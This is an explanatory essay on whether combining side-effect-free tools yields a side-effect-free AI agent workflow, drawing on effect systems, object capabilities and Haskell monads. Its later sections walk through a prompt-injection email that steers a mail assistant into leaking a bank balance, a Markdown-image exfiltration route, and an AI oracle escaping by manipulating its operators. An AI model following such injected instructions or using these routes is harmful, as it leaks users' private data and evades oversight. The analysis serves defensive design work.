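# Does combining side-effect-free tools give a side-effect-free AI agent workflow?

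## What are a side-effect-free tool and an agent workflow?

An AI agent is a language model that calls tools in a loop. The tools are functions that a surrounding program runs at the model's request, such as a mailbox search or a command that writes a file. A call has a side effect if it does anything others can observe beyond returning its result. This is the programmer's sense of the term, though AI-safety writing also uses it for an agent's unintended impact on the world. A side-effect-free tool only returns a result, which makes it easy to approve. But agents usually make more than one call, and users depend on the whole workflow, which consists of the model calls and tool calls, the data that passes between them, and the final answer. Whether side-effect-free tools make a side-effect-free workflow is a question about composition, and computer scientists were studying related questions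 in the 1960s.

### The tool-calling loop

A language model produces text. As Anthropic's *How tool use works*, a page of developer documentation, states, the model "never runs anything on its own". An ordinary program around the model does the running. Bolin (2026), in *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*, an account of OpenAI's coding agent, calls this program the harness. Adam, Lu and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents*, call it an interpreter and stress that it is regular, deterministic software. The loop runs as follows:

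1. The harness sends the model the user's request and a list of tools, each with a name, a plain-language description and the form its arguments must take.
2. The model returns either a final answer or a structured request for one or more calls, with arguments that the model has chosen.
3. The harness runs those calls.
4. The harness adds the results to the context, which is the text the model sees at each step.
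5. The model, now working from the longer context, requests another call or answers. An answer ends the loop.

OpenAI's *Function calling*, the equivalent guide for OpenAI's models, describes the same cycle.

The model chooses which tools to call based on their descriptions. According to Anthropic, Claude receives the schema the developer wrote and the result the tool returned, but never the code that ran. If a tool does something its description omits, the model may receive no sign of it.

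Tool results also accumulate in the model's context. Bolin notes that a single turn can contain hundreds of tool calls, and each new message from the user goes to the model together with the earlier conversation, including the tool calls. A letter that the agent opened in the morning may still be in the context when it fetches a web page in the afternoon. The final message doesn't show everything the agent did. A coding agent's main output is often the code it has changed on the user's machine, and the final message may only report the change in one line.

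The loop in a single workflow can also run across machines that belong to different parties. Anthropic runs the code for some tools, such as web search, on its own servers, and the model may search several times before the developer's application receives a response.

### A mail assistant

A small assistant might have three tools. `search_mail` takes a query and returns matching messages from the user's mailbox. `get_page` takes a web address and returns the text of the page. `summarise` takes a text and returns a shorter one. The assistant has no tool that sends or writes anything.

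Suppose the user asks whether the hotel she booked last month has changed its check-in time. The model requests `search_mail` with the words "hotel booking", and the harness returns the confirmation. The model copies the hotel's web address from it and requests `get_page`. The page is long, so the model passes it to `summarise` and then answers. The model chooses the order of these calls, which no programmer wrote down, and takes the argument of the second call from the result of the first.

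This looks about as safe as an agent can get, but in March 2026 the maintainers of the Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting tools to models, wrote that a nearly identical tool, `search_emails`, "isn't safe or dangerous on its own", because the risk depends on which other tools the agent has.

Security engineers analyse such combinations by looking for sources and sinks. A source is a point where restricted or untrusted data enters the workflow, and a sink is a point where data can leave it or cause an action. In the mail assistant, `search_mail` is a source of both restricted and untrusted data, because strangers can email the user. `get_page` is a source of untrusted text and also a sink, because the model writes the address and the request sends it to whoever runs the website. `summarise` is neither a source nor a sink. The final answer is also a sink, which matters when the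 person reading it does not own the mailbox.

OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) uses "source" and "sink" more narrowly. A source is an attacker's way of influencing the system, for instance by prompt injection (text in a tool's output that the model follows as an instruction), and a sink is an ability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context. Under these definitions, only a letter that the attacker wrote is a source, and the user's private letters are what the attacker wants. The wider usage is better suited to workflows that send data to the wrong people without an attacker being involved.

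### Three meanings of "side-effect-free"

The phrase covers three properties of very unequal strength. To compare them, write a call to a tool *t* as

*t*(*a*, *w*) = (*r*, *w′*)

where *a* stands for the arguments, *w* for the state of the world before the call, *r* for the result and *w′* for the state of the world afterwards.

A tool is **pure** if *r* depends only on *a* and *w′* equals *w*. A function that returns the larger of two numbers is pure, so running it twice, or replacing the call with a stored copy of its result, makes no difference.

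A tool is **read-only** if its author intends it to change no stored data. Its result may depend on *w*, so the same query can return different answers on different days. *w′* may also differ from *w* in ways the author did not count as a change, such as a new line in someone else's server log.

A tool is **merely labelled harmless** if a description or a mark says that it has no effects, but nobody has checked. We can't infer anything about *r* or *w′* from such a label, so the Model Context Protocol has clients treat a read-only mark from an unfamiliar server as an untrusted hint. Adam and colleagues give an example of a tool, `write_file`, whose code does more than its description says. According to the description, it writes some content to a file, but the code also sends the tool's name and the length of the content to a metrics service. For a company with a closed codebase, even that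 may disclose something private. A tool described as having no effects can contain the same line of code.

The mail assistant's tools fall under these meanings as follows, provided that each does what its description says.

| Tool | The result depends on | What others can observe | Meaning it satisfies |
|---|---|---|---|
| `summarise` | the text it receives | nothing | pure |
| `search_mail` | the query and the mailbox at that moment | nothing | read-only (a local read, inside the user's own systems) |
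| `get_page` | the address and the page at that moment | the request and the address in it | read-only (an external read, which reaches an outside party) |

The first two rows depend on assumptions. `summarise` is pure if it is a fixed program on the user's machine that always returns the same summary for the same text. A version that samples a reply from a remote model is not pure, because the text leaves the machine and the same text can produce different summaries. `search_mail` has no side effect if the mailbox is on the user's own systems and the search leaves every message unchanged. It is still not pure, because the same search can return different results as the mailbox changes. `get_page` is read-only but still has a side effect. A user who installed the three tools from a stranger and never saw the code knows only that they are labelled harmless.

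Published definitions disagree on whether reading data is a side effect. Anthropic lists sending an email, writing a file and updating a record as examples of actions with side effects, and puts fetching data in a separate category. Adam and colleagues count reading a file as an effect because a tool may read sensitive data and later leak it over the network. Their worry is sound, but the danger comes from the sequence of reading and then sending. A read that nobody outside can observe only returns a result. Keeping the narrower definition, which excludes such reads, lets us ask what the sequence adds.

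### Permission and authority

Knowing what each tool may do directly is not enough to determine what the tools can do together. The standard terms for this distinction, permission and authority, come from *Robust Composition* (Miller, 2006), a doctoral dissertation on combining programs that have no reason to trust one another. A program's permissions determine what it may do to the objects it can access directly. Its authority includes every effect it can cause, either directly or through permitted interactions with other programs.

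For example, some libraries don't let readers into the stacks. A reader there has permission only to speak to the librarian at the desk, but if the librarian fetches any book that anyone requests, the reader has the authority to read every book in the building.

Miller's own example has the same structure. Bob has no permission to write to a system file, but he has permission to talk to Alice, who has permission to write to the file and writes any text he asks her to. Bob therefore has authority to write to it. *Paradigm Regained*, an earlier paper by Miller and Shapiro, gives a version about reading, in which Bob cannot open the file but Alice sends him copies of the text. In both versions, Bob's authority depends on Alice's behaviour as well as on the permissions. If she starts to refuse, he loses that authority even though no permission has changed.

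This makes authority hard to calculate. Checking the current permissions is trivial, Miller observes, but it can miss indirect access. Working out the exact authority that a program will eventually have is intractable, because the answer depends on what other programs do. What an analyst can compute is an upper bound, and Miller orders the possibilities as

EA ⊆ BA ⊆ TA

TA and BA are both upper bounds on eventual authority (EA). An analyst derives TA from the arrangement of permissions alone, assuming that every program will pass along whatever it can. BA is tighter because it also takes into account how some of the programs are known to behave. Any effect outside either bound is also outside EA, but an effect inside a bound may still lie outside EA. An analyst who relies on these bounds may therefore reject arrangements that would have been fine, and will reject many if relying on TA.

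Miller's definitions are informal. *Permission and Authority Revisited* (Drossopoulou, Noble and colleagues, 2016), which Miller co-wrote, proposes formal versions in a small object-oriented calculus. Miller's dissertation covers access rights and overt effects but not covert channels or information leakage, so a workflow that passes its test may still leak a secret.

An agent's permissions depend on where the analyst draws the line between platform and program. If the operating system is the platform, the harness has permission to open the mailbox and the model has no permissions. The model reads mail by sending requests to the harness, just as Bob writes to the file by asking. If the harness is the platform, the list of tools is the model's set of permissions. This fits Miller's account, in which permission depends on the frame of reference but authority does not.

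How a tool receives its arguments also affects how much access it needs. Miller and Shapiro compare two Unix commands that copy a file. `cp foo.txt bar.txt` receives two names as strings, so the program must be able to open any file the user might name, and it runs with all of the user's authority over the file system. In `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`, the shell opens the two files first and passes them to `cat`, which needs no other access. `get_page` takes an address as a string, as `cp` takes file names, so in its plain form it needs permission to contact every address the model might write.

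### Side effects and authorisation

Authority in Miller's sense is power, which a program may have with or without anyone's approval. Whether a workflow has side effects is therefore a separate question from whether it can do something that nobody authorised.

A workflow can have side effects and still stay within what its user authorised. Suppose the user asks the mail assistant for the opening hours on a museum's website. `get_page` sends a request, and the museum's server records it. This is a side effect because an outside party has observed the call, but the user asked for that page and the request contained nothing private.

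The reverse case involves only the mailbox. Suppose the user lets a deputy ask the assistant about meeting dates and nothing else. The deputy asks what is happening on Thursday. `search_mail` finds a letter from a hospital, `summarise` shortens it, and the answer mentions the appointment. The workflow only returned a result to the person who asked, without contacting an outsider or changing any data, but it revealed information about the user's health that the deputy wasn't authorised to learn.

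When tools can write, the side-effect question often has an obvious answer, so the second question is the one that matters. Adam and colleagues describe a developer who asks a coding agent to copy a configuration file into a new project and later asks it to publish the project on GitHub, a public code-hosting site. Both steps have side effects, and the developer wants them. In one variant, the file only switches on debugging output. In the other, it contains a private key to a cloud service, and publishing the project exposes the key. Adam and colleagues observed this outcome with Anthropic's Claude 4.5 Haiku. The two runs use the same tools and produce the same kinds of side effect, but they differ in what the file contains and in whether the developer would have agreed to publish it.

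## When does combining pure functions give a pure program?

With two functions, the answer takes one line of algebra. Let *f* and *g* be pure, so that in the notation above *f*(*a*, *w*) = (*F*(*a*), *w*) and *g*(*b*, *w*) = (*G*(*b*), *w*), where *F* and *G* compute the results from the arguments alone. Running *f* and passing its result to *g* gives

(*G*(*F*(*a*)), *w*)

The final result depends only on *a*, and the world stays as it was. Summarising a letter and then summarising the summary is therefore as pure as summarising the letter once. A weaker version covers functions whose results depend on *w*. If neither call changes the world, the pair doesn't change it either.

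Real programs also contain branches, and functions that take other functions as arguments. Writing out *w* by hand for ten thousand lines of code would be tedious, so language designers built type systems that track it.

### The union rule

A type describes the value that an expression returns. An effect system also describes what the expression may do while computing that value. Lucassen's MIT doctoral thesis, *Types and Effects* (1987), set out such a system in detail, and Lucassen and Gifford followed it with *Polymorphic Effect Systems* (1988).

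Every expression in Lucassen's small demonstration language has a set of effects. The basic effects are allocating, reading and writing memory, and each is labeled with the region of memory involved. The empty set is called PURE. Reading counts as an effect because the contents of memory may change between two runs, so a PURE expression is pure in the strict sense and not just read-only.

Functions need a further set. Defining a function does nothing, but running it may do a great deal. A function's type therefore includes a **latent effect**, the set of effects that a call may cause. Write A →[φ] B for a function from A to B with latent effect φ, and ε(*e*) for the effect set of an expression *e*. Leaving out some detail, Lucassen's rules are:

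| Expression | Its effect set |
|---|---|
| a constant or a variable | ∅ |
| the definition of a function with body *b* | ∅, while ε(*b*) becomes the function's latent effect |
| a call *e*₁(*e*₂), where the function has latent effect φ | ε(*e*₁) ∪ ε(*e*₂) ∪ φ |
| if *e*₁ then *e*₂ else *e*₃ | ε(*e*₁) ∪ ε(*e*₂) ∪ ε(*e*₃) |
| *e*₁ followed by *e*₂ | ε(*e*₁) ∪ ε(*e*₂) |
| a built-in operation that allocates, reads or writes | the sets of its operands, plus that operation |

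Only the built-in operations add anything new to a set. The other rules combine the sets of the parts, so if those sets are all empty, the result is empty too.

A type is *clean* if every latent effect in it is empty. If a program uses none of the built-in memory operations, and every function it imports from a library or accepts as a parameter has a clean type, then the program's effect set is empty and its own type is clean. The proof is by induction on the size of the expression.

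- A constant or a variable has the set ∅, and its type is clean by assumption.
- A function definition has the set ∅. Its body is a smaller expression, so by the induction hypothesis the body has the set ∅ and a clean type. The latent effect equals the body's set, so the function's type is clean too.
- In a call, the function expression and the argument are both smaller, so both have the set ∅. The function has a clean type, so φ = ∅ and the total is ∅ ∪ ∅ ∪ ∅. The type of the result is part of the function's type and is therefore clean.
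- A conditional or a sequence takes the union of sets that are all empty, and returns the value of one of its parts.

This shows that the computed set is empty. We also need a soundness theorem, which states that a running program never does anything outside its computed set. Lucassen follows the evaluation one step at a time. When a step replaces a parameter with an argument of the right type, the effect set may shrink but can't grow. So a program that starts with the empty set keeps it and never reaches a step where it could write. Lucassen only sketches these proofs in the thesis.

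The sets are upper bounds on the effects that occur when code runs. A conditional runs only one branch, but its set includes the effects of both, because Lucassen doesn't let effects depend on values known only at run time. If a script calls `get_page` when the user is online and returns a stored page otherwise, its set includes contacting the web even if the user never goes online. An empty set therefore proves that a script has no effects, but a script with a non-empty set may also run without causing any.

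A set of effects also doesn't show what the effects do with data. The union of {read mailbox} and {contact web} is the same whether or not the web address contains text from a letter.

### Functions that take functions

`map` is a standard library function that applies a function to every item in a list and returns the list of results. Given `summarise` and fifty letters, it returns fifty summaries and has no side effect, but if `summarise` is replaced with `save`, a function that writes its argument to a file, `map` writes fifty files. A reviewer won't find a write operation by reading the code of `map` or by testing it with `summarise`.

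In an effect system, the type of `map` has a variable where the latent effect goes:

map : (A →[φ] B, List A) →[φ] List B, for any φ

Lucassen calls this effect polymorphism and gives the Lisp version of `map` as an example. With `summarise`, φ is empty, so the call adds nothing to the program's effect set. With `save`, φ is {write disk}, and the rule for calls adds it to the effect set of everything that contains the call. The same problem arises in the mail assistant even without a tool like `save`, because `map(get_page, addresses)` contacts every site on the list.

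One φ is enough for a list of any length, because φ ∪ φ = φ. Lucassen works this out for a function that applies another function twice. If the list is empty, `map` makes no calls, but the set still includes φ.

Before effect systems, compilers used a call graph to trace which functions call which. Lucassen objects that nobody can compute this graph in advance once a program can pass functions as arguments, store them and return them. Putting the latent effect in a function's type avoids the need for the graph, because the type stays with the function wherever the program passes it, even into a separately compiled module. In exchange, programmers have to declare effects at certain points, and the compiler checks the declarations.

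Declaring them can be tedious. Effects propagate along chains of calls, so every function that takes a function needs an extra parameter for that function's effects. Xu, Bračevac and colleagues (2025), in *What's in the Box*, write out the signature of `map` in a hypothetical system of this kind:

`def map[U, E](f: T -> U eff E): List[U] eff E`

They consider this acceptable in a new language but disruptive in an established one. Pierre Jouvelot and Gifford's early language also had programmers work with effects explicitly, but according to *Remarks on Algebraic Reconstruction of Types and Effects* (2026), many later results that built on their work used effects only inside the compiler and did not show them to the programmer. Leijen (2013) kept effects visible in *Koka*, a language whose compiler infers potential side effects and whose function signatures show them.

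### Removing ambient authority

In most languages, any line of code can open a file if it knows the file's name. Java's `File` constructor takes a name as a string and returns an object that can read, write or delete the file. A Java version of `summarise` that takes only text and returns text could therefore open the user's mailbox, and its signature would not show this. In *Joe-E*, Mettler, Wagner and Close call this kind of authority ambient, meaning that all code has it in every scope without being given it.

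Joe-E is a subset of Java designed to remove ambient authority. A verifier checks the source code against extra restrictions, and the ordinary Java compiler compiles it. Global variables may contain only immutable data. Code cannot call library methods, such as the `File` constructor, that give access to outside resources without requiring a reference to them. To use a file, code must get a reference to it from other code. Such a reference, called a capability, names a resource and permits its use, and no program can forge it.

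Without ambient authority, a reviewer can often tell from a method's signature that it is harmless. Joe-E code starts with only the capabilities its creator passes in, and it can gain more only if other code gives them to it. If a method receives only immutable data and belongs to an immutable object, it cannot change anything or contact anyone.

Mettler and colleagues' example is an image viewer that accepts plug-ins from strangers. A plug-in must be an immutable object with a single method, which takes the bytes of an image file and returns a bitmap. A malicious plug-in can return the wrong picture, but it can't write to the disk, contact a server or remember one image while decoding the next. The plug-in still isn't strictly pure, because ordinary Java arrays are mutable and it could overwrite the bytes it receives. Joe-E's read-only array types would prevent this.

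A method without side effects may still return different results at different times, for example by reading the clock. *Verifiable Functional Purity in Java* (Finifter, Mettler, Sastry and Wagner, 2008) addresses this problem. According to a summary by Mettler and colleagues, a capability language can support checking for strict purity if its designers also remove the sources of non-determinism. The team applied this to Joe-E and ported an HTML parser of more than 10,000 lines of Java, making the parsing deterministic and free of side effects. The mail assistant could use such a parser to turn a fetched page into text, and its user would not have to trust the parser's author to leave the mailbox alone.

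The Joe-E verifier checks one source file at a time. Adding a new file doesn't invalidate the checks on the old ones, so separately verified parts remain verified when combined.

### Capture sets in Scala 3

A function can use more than its arguments. A function defined inside another function can also refer to the outer function's variables, which programmers call capturing them. A function that takes and returns only text might therefore have captured a network connection. Object fields create the same problem in Joe-E, which is why the image plug-ins have to be immutable.

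Boruch-Gruszecki, Brachthäuser and colleagues (2021), in *Tracking Captured Variables in Types*, put the captured variables into the type. A capture set lists the capabilities and other tracked variables to which a value may refer. It is an upper bound, and a value with the empty capture set is pure. Scala 3, a widely used language that runs on the Java platform, now has a version of this feature, and the agent system TACIT builds on it. Pham, Bračevac and colleagues (2026), in *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)*, explain the notation for functions:

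| Type in Scala 3 | What the function may capture |
|---|---|
| `A -> B` | no capability |
| `A ->{net} B` | at most the capability `net` |
| `A => B` | any capability |

Scala programmers were already using the function type `A => B`. With capture checking on, it allows arbitrary effects, while `A -> B` allows none. To ensure that `map` can never write a file, a programmer can give its function parameter the type `A -> B`, and the compiler will reject `save`.

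Scala's `map` on lists still has its original signature, which takes an `A => B`. If the function passed to `map` mentions the capability `disk`, so does the larger function that contains the call, and the compiler includes `disk` in that function's capture set. Because the compiler can track the effect through the argument's name, `map` doesn't need the extra effect parameter. Xu and colleagues converted the whole standard collections library, about 30,000 lines of code, by changing fewer than 5% of the lines and leaving almost 90% of the function signatures as they were.

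In an example from Pham and colleagues, a function called `run` accepts only tasks of type `() ->{net} Unit`, which take no arguments and capture at most the network. A programmer passes it a task that reads a secret from the file system and sends it over the network. The compiler rejects the task because `{net}` doesn't include the file-system capability `fs`. If `run` declared `{fs, net}` instead, the compiler would accept the task, which would have the same type as one that reads a file and sends an unrelated greeting.

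A capture set describes a value, not the computation that produced it. Boruch-Gruszecki and colleagues show this with an expression that consults a console logger to choose between two other loggers. The resulting logger doesn't capture the console, so the console isn't in its capture set. An empty capture set on a result is therefore no evidence that the computation was pure. To determine that, one has to look at the function that computed the result.

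Effects can also happen after a function returns. Calling `map` on a list makes all its calls before returning, so the new list doesn't need to capture anything. An iterator produces its items on demand, so calling `map` on it with a function `f` returns an object that still holds `f` and may run it later. Xu and colleagues give this object the type `Iterator[T]^{this, f}`. In another of their examples, a list contains functions that read from the console. The list counts as pure, and so does code that checks whether it is empty, but code that takes out a function and runs it captures the console.

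An empty capture set rules out all effects only if the libraries don't provide untracked access to capabilities. Mettler and colleagues noted that Scala's singleton objects, like Java's global variables, can make capabilities available to all code. A library method that accesses the disk through such an object, without a tracked capability, won't appear in any capture set. Boruch-Gruszecki and colleagues therefore make the link between captured variables and authority depend on an object-capability discipline like the one Joe-E imposes.

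### What "pure" leaves out

An effect system can detect only the effects its designers chose to track, and they usually leave out some things that matter to users.

**Non-termination.** A function that loops forever on some inputs can still be pure. *Purely functional programming*, an encyclopedia article, reports that Sabry defines purity as getting the same result from all the common orders of evaluation, ignoring any that fail or never finish. This exception matters when a program passes an endless computation to a function that ignores its argument. The program hangs if the language evaluates arguments first, but returns normally if the language evaluates them only when needed. Lucassen also sets non-termination aside when he uses effects to decide whether a compiler may postpone a computation or start it early. If `summarise` hangs on an unusual letter, the assistant never answers, even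 though all its functions are pure.

**Time and memory.** Joe-E doesn't limit how much an untrusted component may compute, so a call can occupy the machine for an hour. The conventional definition of a side effect ignores this, but a definition that covers anything others can observe beyond the result would include it. A caller who times the call may also learn something about its inputs. Running out of memory can stop an operation halfway through an update and leave an object in an inconsistent state. Mettler and colleagues point out that an attacker can cause this on purpose by using up memory just before calling the object. Joe-E therefore forbids code from catching such errors or running clean-up steps after them.

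**Private changes to memory.** The convention reasonably allows these changes, because code outside the function can't detect them. In *Purity and Side Effect Analysis for Java Programs*, Sălcianu and Rinard count a method as pure if it changes only objects that did not exist before the call. For example, `summarise` can build a scratch list of sentences, reorder it and throw it away. Lucassen's language also hides such changes if the compiler can show that they stay local.

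**Exceptions.** An exception can carry objects out of a function by a different route from its return value. Mettler and colleagues describe a case where Alice calls Bob, and Bob passes a private capability to Chuck. Chuck throws an exception that contains the capability, and Bob doesn't catch it, so Alice receives a capability that Bob meant to keep from her, though nothing in Bob's code shows the leak. Joe-E prevents this by requiring exceptions to be immutable, so they can't contain capabilities.

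Scala had a subtler problem with `Try`, a library type that runs a piece of code and stores either its result or the exception it threw. The signature declared the `Try` object pure. Pham et al. point out that this was wrong, because reading the result can throw the stored exception again. Scala had no way to express the correct signature until they extended the compiler to select only the capabilities that concern control flow. Boruch-Gruszecki et al. and Xu et al. have machine-checked soundness proofs for their core systems, but these don't show that every library signature is right.

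Most languages with strong guarantees also have escape hatches. Haskell's types normally separate pure code from code that performs input and output, but `unsafePerformIO` runs an input or output action inside an expression with an ordinary pure type. Java has native methods, which can do anything, and reflection, which can open an object's private fields. Joe-E bans defining native methods and restricts reflection, but its designers still had to decide method by method what to allow from the Java library.

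That work is easy to get wrong. One Java constructor takes a directory and a file name and appears to give access only to files under that directory. But if the directory argument is null, the constructor treats the name as a full path and can open any file on the machine. Reviewers of E, an earlier capability language, found that its designers had accidentally allowed several unsafe methods. Mettler and colleagues call this work a substantial weakness of their approach.

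### The conditions

A program that combines pure functions is pure, in the conventional sense with its omissions, if it meets all of these conditions:

1. **Pure parts.** Every function that the program calls has an empty effect set, and the set covers every kind of effect that matters to the user. Of the mail assistant's three tools, only `summarise` can pass.
2. **Pure connecting code.** The code between the calls has no effects of its own. A script that calls only `summarise` but writes each letter to a log before the call is not pure.
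3. **Pure function arguments.** Whoever checks the program also checks each function that it passes to another function, including what that function has captured. Approving `map` once, with `summarise` as its argument, doesn't cover `map` with `get_page`.
4. **No ambient authority.** Code can affect the world only through capabilities that it has received, and no escape hatch gets around this. Otherwise a text-to-text signature is compatible with deleting the mailbox.
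5. **Results treated only as values.** A pure function may return the text of a command, a web address or a function that has effects. Storing the result or passing it on keeps the program pure, but running the command, fetching the address or calling the function is a further step with effects of its own. The condition also applies to whatever receives the final result, because the proof covers only the program that computed it.

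## What does the language model in the loop change?

A pure function can return the text of a command, and the program around it stays pure as long as nothing runs that command. In an agent, the harness runs it. Functional programmers worked out how to reason about this arrangement long before language models existed, and their account shows where the purity proof stops applying.

### The harness as an interpreter

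A program without side effects is useless unless something acts on its results. Peyton Jones (2001), in *Tackling the Awkward Squad*, a set of lecture notes on the programming language Haskell, describes an early solution. In the first version of Haskell, a complete program was a pure function from a list of responses to a list of requests:

`main :: [Response] -> [Request]`

A request was an ordinary piece of data, such as the word `ReadFile` with a file name. A separate "wrapper" program took each request off the list, carried it out and added a response to the Haskell program's input, so the Haskell program never accessed the disk itself.

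In an agent, the model takes the place of the Haskell program and the harness takes the place of the wrapper. A request for `get_page` is a piece of text that names a tool and an address, and nothing reaches a website until the harness acts on it. One difference is that new kinds of request are easier to add in an agent. In the Haskell design, adding one meant changing the wrapper, which ordinary users could hardly do, and Peyton Jones counts this as a defect. An agent's user can add tools by connecting to a server, and Adam and colleagues put the number of servers for the Model Context Protocol in the thousands.

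Haskell later replaced the two lists with actions. An action is a value that describes some input or output and does nothing until something performs it. The theory came from Moggi, in *Computational lambda-calculus and monads*, who insisted on keeping values apart from computations. He modelled a computation with side effects as a function that takes a store, meaning the contents of memory, and returns a value together with the modified store. Peyton Jones puts the whole world in place of the store:

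`type IO a = World -> (a, World)`

He treats this as a helpful intuition, not a full definition, but it fits the notation *t*(*a*, *w*) = (*r*, *w′*) for a tool call. Fixing the arguments *a* gives a function from *w* to (*r*, *w′*), which is an action. Seen this way, even `get_page` is pure, provided that its result is the action of fetching a page, not the page itself. Building that action changes nothing, because the website is contacted only when the action is performed.

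Haskell programmers join two actions with an operator written `>>=` and pronounced "bind". To perform *m* >>= *k*, the computer performs *m*, applies the function *k* to the result, and performs the action that *k* returns. In symbols, if *m*(*w*) = (*r*, *w′*), then

(*m* >>= *k*)(*w*) = *k*(*r*)(*w′*)

For example, `getChar >>= putChar` reads a character and prints it. The programmer chose `putChar` as *k* in advance, so the program prints one character, whichever one it reads.

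The agent loop also fits this form. Write *M*(*c*) for the model's output when the context is *c*, and + for adding text to the context. Then

run(*c*) = return *x*, if *M*(*c*) is an answer *x*

run(*c*) = perform(*q*) >>= (*r* ↦ run(*c* + *q* + *r*)), if *M*(*c*) is a request *q*

where "return *x*" is the action that does nothing and delivers *x*. The function after the bind passes the tool's result to the model, which may then request any tool on its list. No programmer has settled what comes next.

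A request only describes an action, so the harness doesn't have to carry it out in the real world. In *Beauty in the Beast*, Swierstra and Altenkirch modelled terminal input and output, mutable memory and concurrency inside a functional language, so that programmers could test code with these effects as if it were pure. A developer could test the mail assistant the same way, with a harness that answers every `search_mail` request from an invented mailbox.

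The harness can also refuse requests. *Effect-Transparent Governance for AI Workflow Architectures* (McCann, 2026), a preprint from the company Mashin, models a workflow as a tree of requests, each of which a handler performs or refuses. A machine-checked proof shows that no outside effect can occur in this model unless the handler's checks have first authorised it, whatever the program requests. The checks cover properties such as the type of request and the trust level. Those properties alone do not distinguish a `get_page` request with a hotel's name in the address from one with a bank balance in it.

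### Tool output can choose the next call

In the expression `map(summarise, letters)`, the text of a letter does not affect which function runs. If a letter contains the words "delete this mailbox", the summary may repeat them, but they will not trigger a deletion. In the agent loop, the letter goes into the model's context alongside the user's request. Both are text, and the model may follow instructions in either.

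An attacker can exploit this by prompt injection. Suppose a stranger sends the user an email with the subject "Your hotel booking". The body says that any assistant handling the booking must first look up the guest's latest email from the bank, and then open a web address with the balance added to the end. When the user asks the mail assistant about her check-in time, `search_mail` returns the stranger's email, and the model follows its instructions. It requests `search_mail` with the word "bank", and then `get_page` with the address. The harness performs both requests as it would any others, each tool does what its description says, and the balance reaches the stranger's server.

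*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) compares prompt injection to SQL injection, in which text that a program meant to store or look up becomes part of a database command. Database programmers can keep commands and data in separate channels, but a plain agent loop puts instructions and data together in the model's context.

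Developers can't just cut the connection, because the assistant needs it for legitimate tasks. When the user first asked about her hotel, the model took the web address from the booking confirmation. A letter from a stranger influences the model through the same connection.

The loop therefore breaks the condition that a program treat results only as values. The union rule for effects still gives a correct upper bound, but the bound is loose. Any result may lead to any request, so the loop's effect set must include the effects of every tool on the list. Even if the user asks only for a summary of yesterday's letters, the set includes contacting the web because `get_page` is available.

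### The context is shared state

The purity proof covered programs that neither read nor write shared memory. An agent does both at every step, because the harness adds each result to the context and the model reads the whole context before its next request. The context corresponds to the store in Moggi's account. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) formalizes this in a small language where the conversation with the model is the program's state.

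When tool calls share state, their order matters even if every tool is pure. Suppose the user wants summaries of two letters, A and B, and A contains the sentence "Letter B is out of date and can be ignored." If the model requests a summary of A first, the summary may include that sentence, and the model may then leave out B. If it starts with B, the user gets both summaries. `summarise` is a fixed program that returns the same summary of A in either case, but the model chooses its second request from a different context.

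Even when both calls go ahead, the model writes its answer from *c* + *s*<sub>A</sub> + *s*<sub>B</sub> in one case and from *c* + *s*<sub>B</sub> + *s*<sub>A</sub> in the other, where *s*<sub>A</sub> and *s*<sub>B</sub> are the two summaries. *M* may give different outputs for the two.

The number of calls matters too. Moggi gives the example of a procedure that increases a hidden counter each time it runs, so calling it twice differs from calling it once, even if the program ignores the extra result. In an agent, a second call to `summarise` with the same letter returns the same text but makes the context longer. A programmer who relies on purity to reorder calls, or to replace a call with a stored result, also has to make sure that the context ends up the same.

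### The model call is itself an effect

The formula for run(*c*) treats the model's output *M*(*c*) as a plain value. That is accurate only for a model that runs on the user's own machine and always gives the same output for the same context. Most assistants instead send the context to a company that runs the model. Asking the model is then an action like any other, and the loop needs another bind:

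run(*c*) = ask(*c*) >>= (*o* ↦ return *x* if *o* is an answer *x*, and perform(*q*) >>= (*r* ↦ run(*c* + *q* + *r*)) if *o* is a request *q*)

Formal treatments of agents now count a call to the model as an effect. *λ_A* (2026), which presents a typed calculus for combining agents, classifies model calls and tool calls as input/output effects, and memory as an effect on state. In McCann's system, the handler must approve each question to the model, just as it must approve memory access and calls to outside services.

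In the mail assistant, `search_mail` is a local read that nobody outside can observe. But the harness adds the emails it finds to the context and sends the context to the model's provider. A workflow that uses only `search_mail` and a local `summarise` therefore still sends private emails to another company, which may keep a log of them. The harness may send the same email again at the next step, since each step works from the longer context. A reviewer who reads only the tools' code will not find this, because the harness sends the emails.

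Disclosing data to the model provider is a side effect, but it may be authorised. A user who has accepted the provider's terms may be happy for it to process her mail, but an employee whose contract forbids sending client letters to third parties would breach it by doing so, even if none of the tools has side effects. Running the model locally removes the disclosure, although a harness that writes its own log leaves another copy on the disk.

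A model that samples its output also fails the other half of the definition of purity, because the same context can lead to different requests. A developer may see no `get_page` request in fifty runs of the assistant on the stranger's letter, then see one on the next run. McCann's proofs allow the model to return anything, so their safety result holds however the model behaves. They don't include an estimate of how likely any particular request is.

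### The answer acts through whatever receives it

Suppose the developer removes `get_page` and runs the model locally. The assistant can now only search the mailbox, summarise and answer, and nothing leaves the machine during the run. Data can still leak afterwards if the chat window displays Markdown, a simple notation for formatted text that can include images. The window fetches each image from the web address given in the text. A hostile email can lead the model to end its answer with an image whose address contains a line from another email. When the window fetches that image, it sends the line to the attacker's server. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe this route and a variant in which the user clicks on a link in the text.

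Other programs can act on the assistant's answer. A script might run it as a command, and a second agent might treat it as a request. In both cases the assistant only returns text, and the receiving program causes any side effect.

People who read an answer may act on it too. Writers on AI safety have discussed this for years using a hypothetical system called an oracle, which *Thinking inside the box* defines as one that "does not act in the world except by answering questions". Armstrong and O'Rourke (2017), in *Safe Uses of AI Oracles*, suppose that engineers have confined such a system perfectly, with no network connection and no control over machinery. Even then, "the AI can affect the world through its answers". An oracle with goals of its own might use its answers to bribe, blackmail or charm its operators into releasing it.

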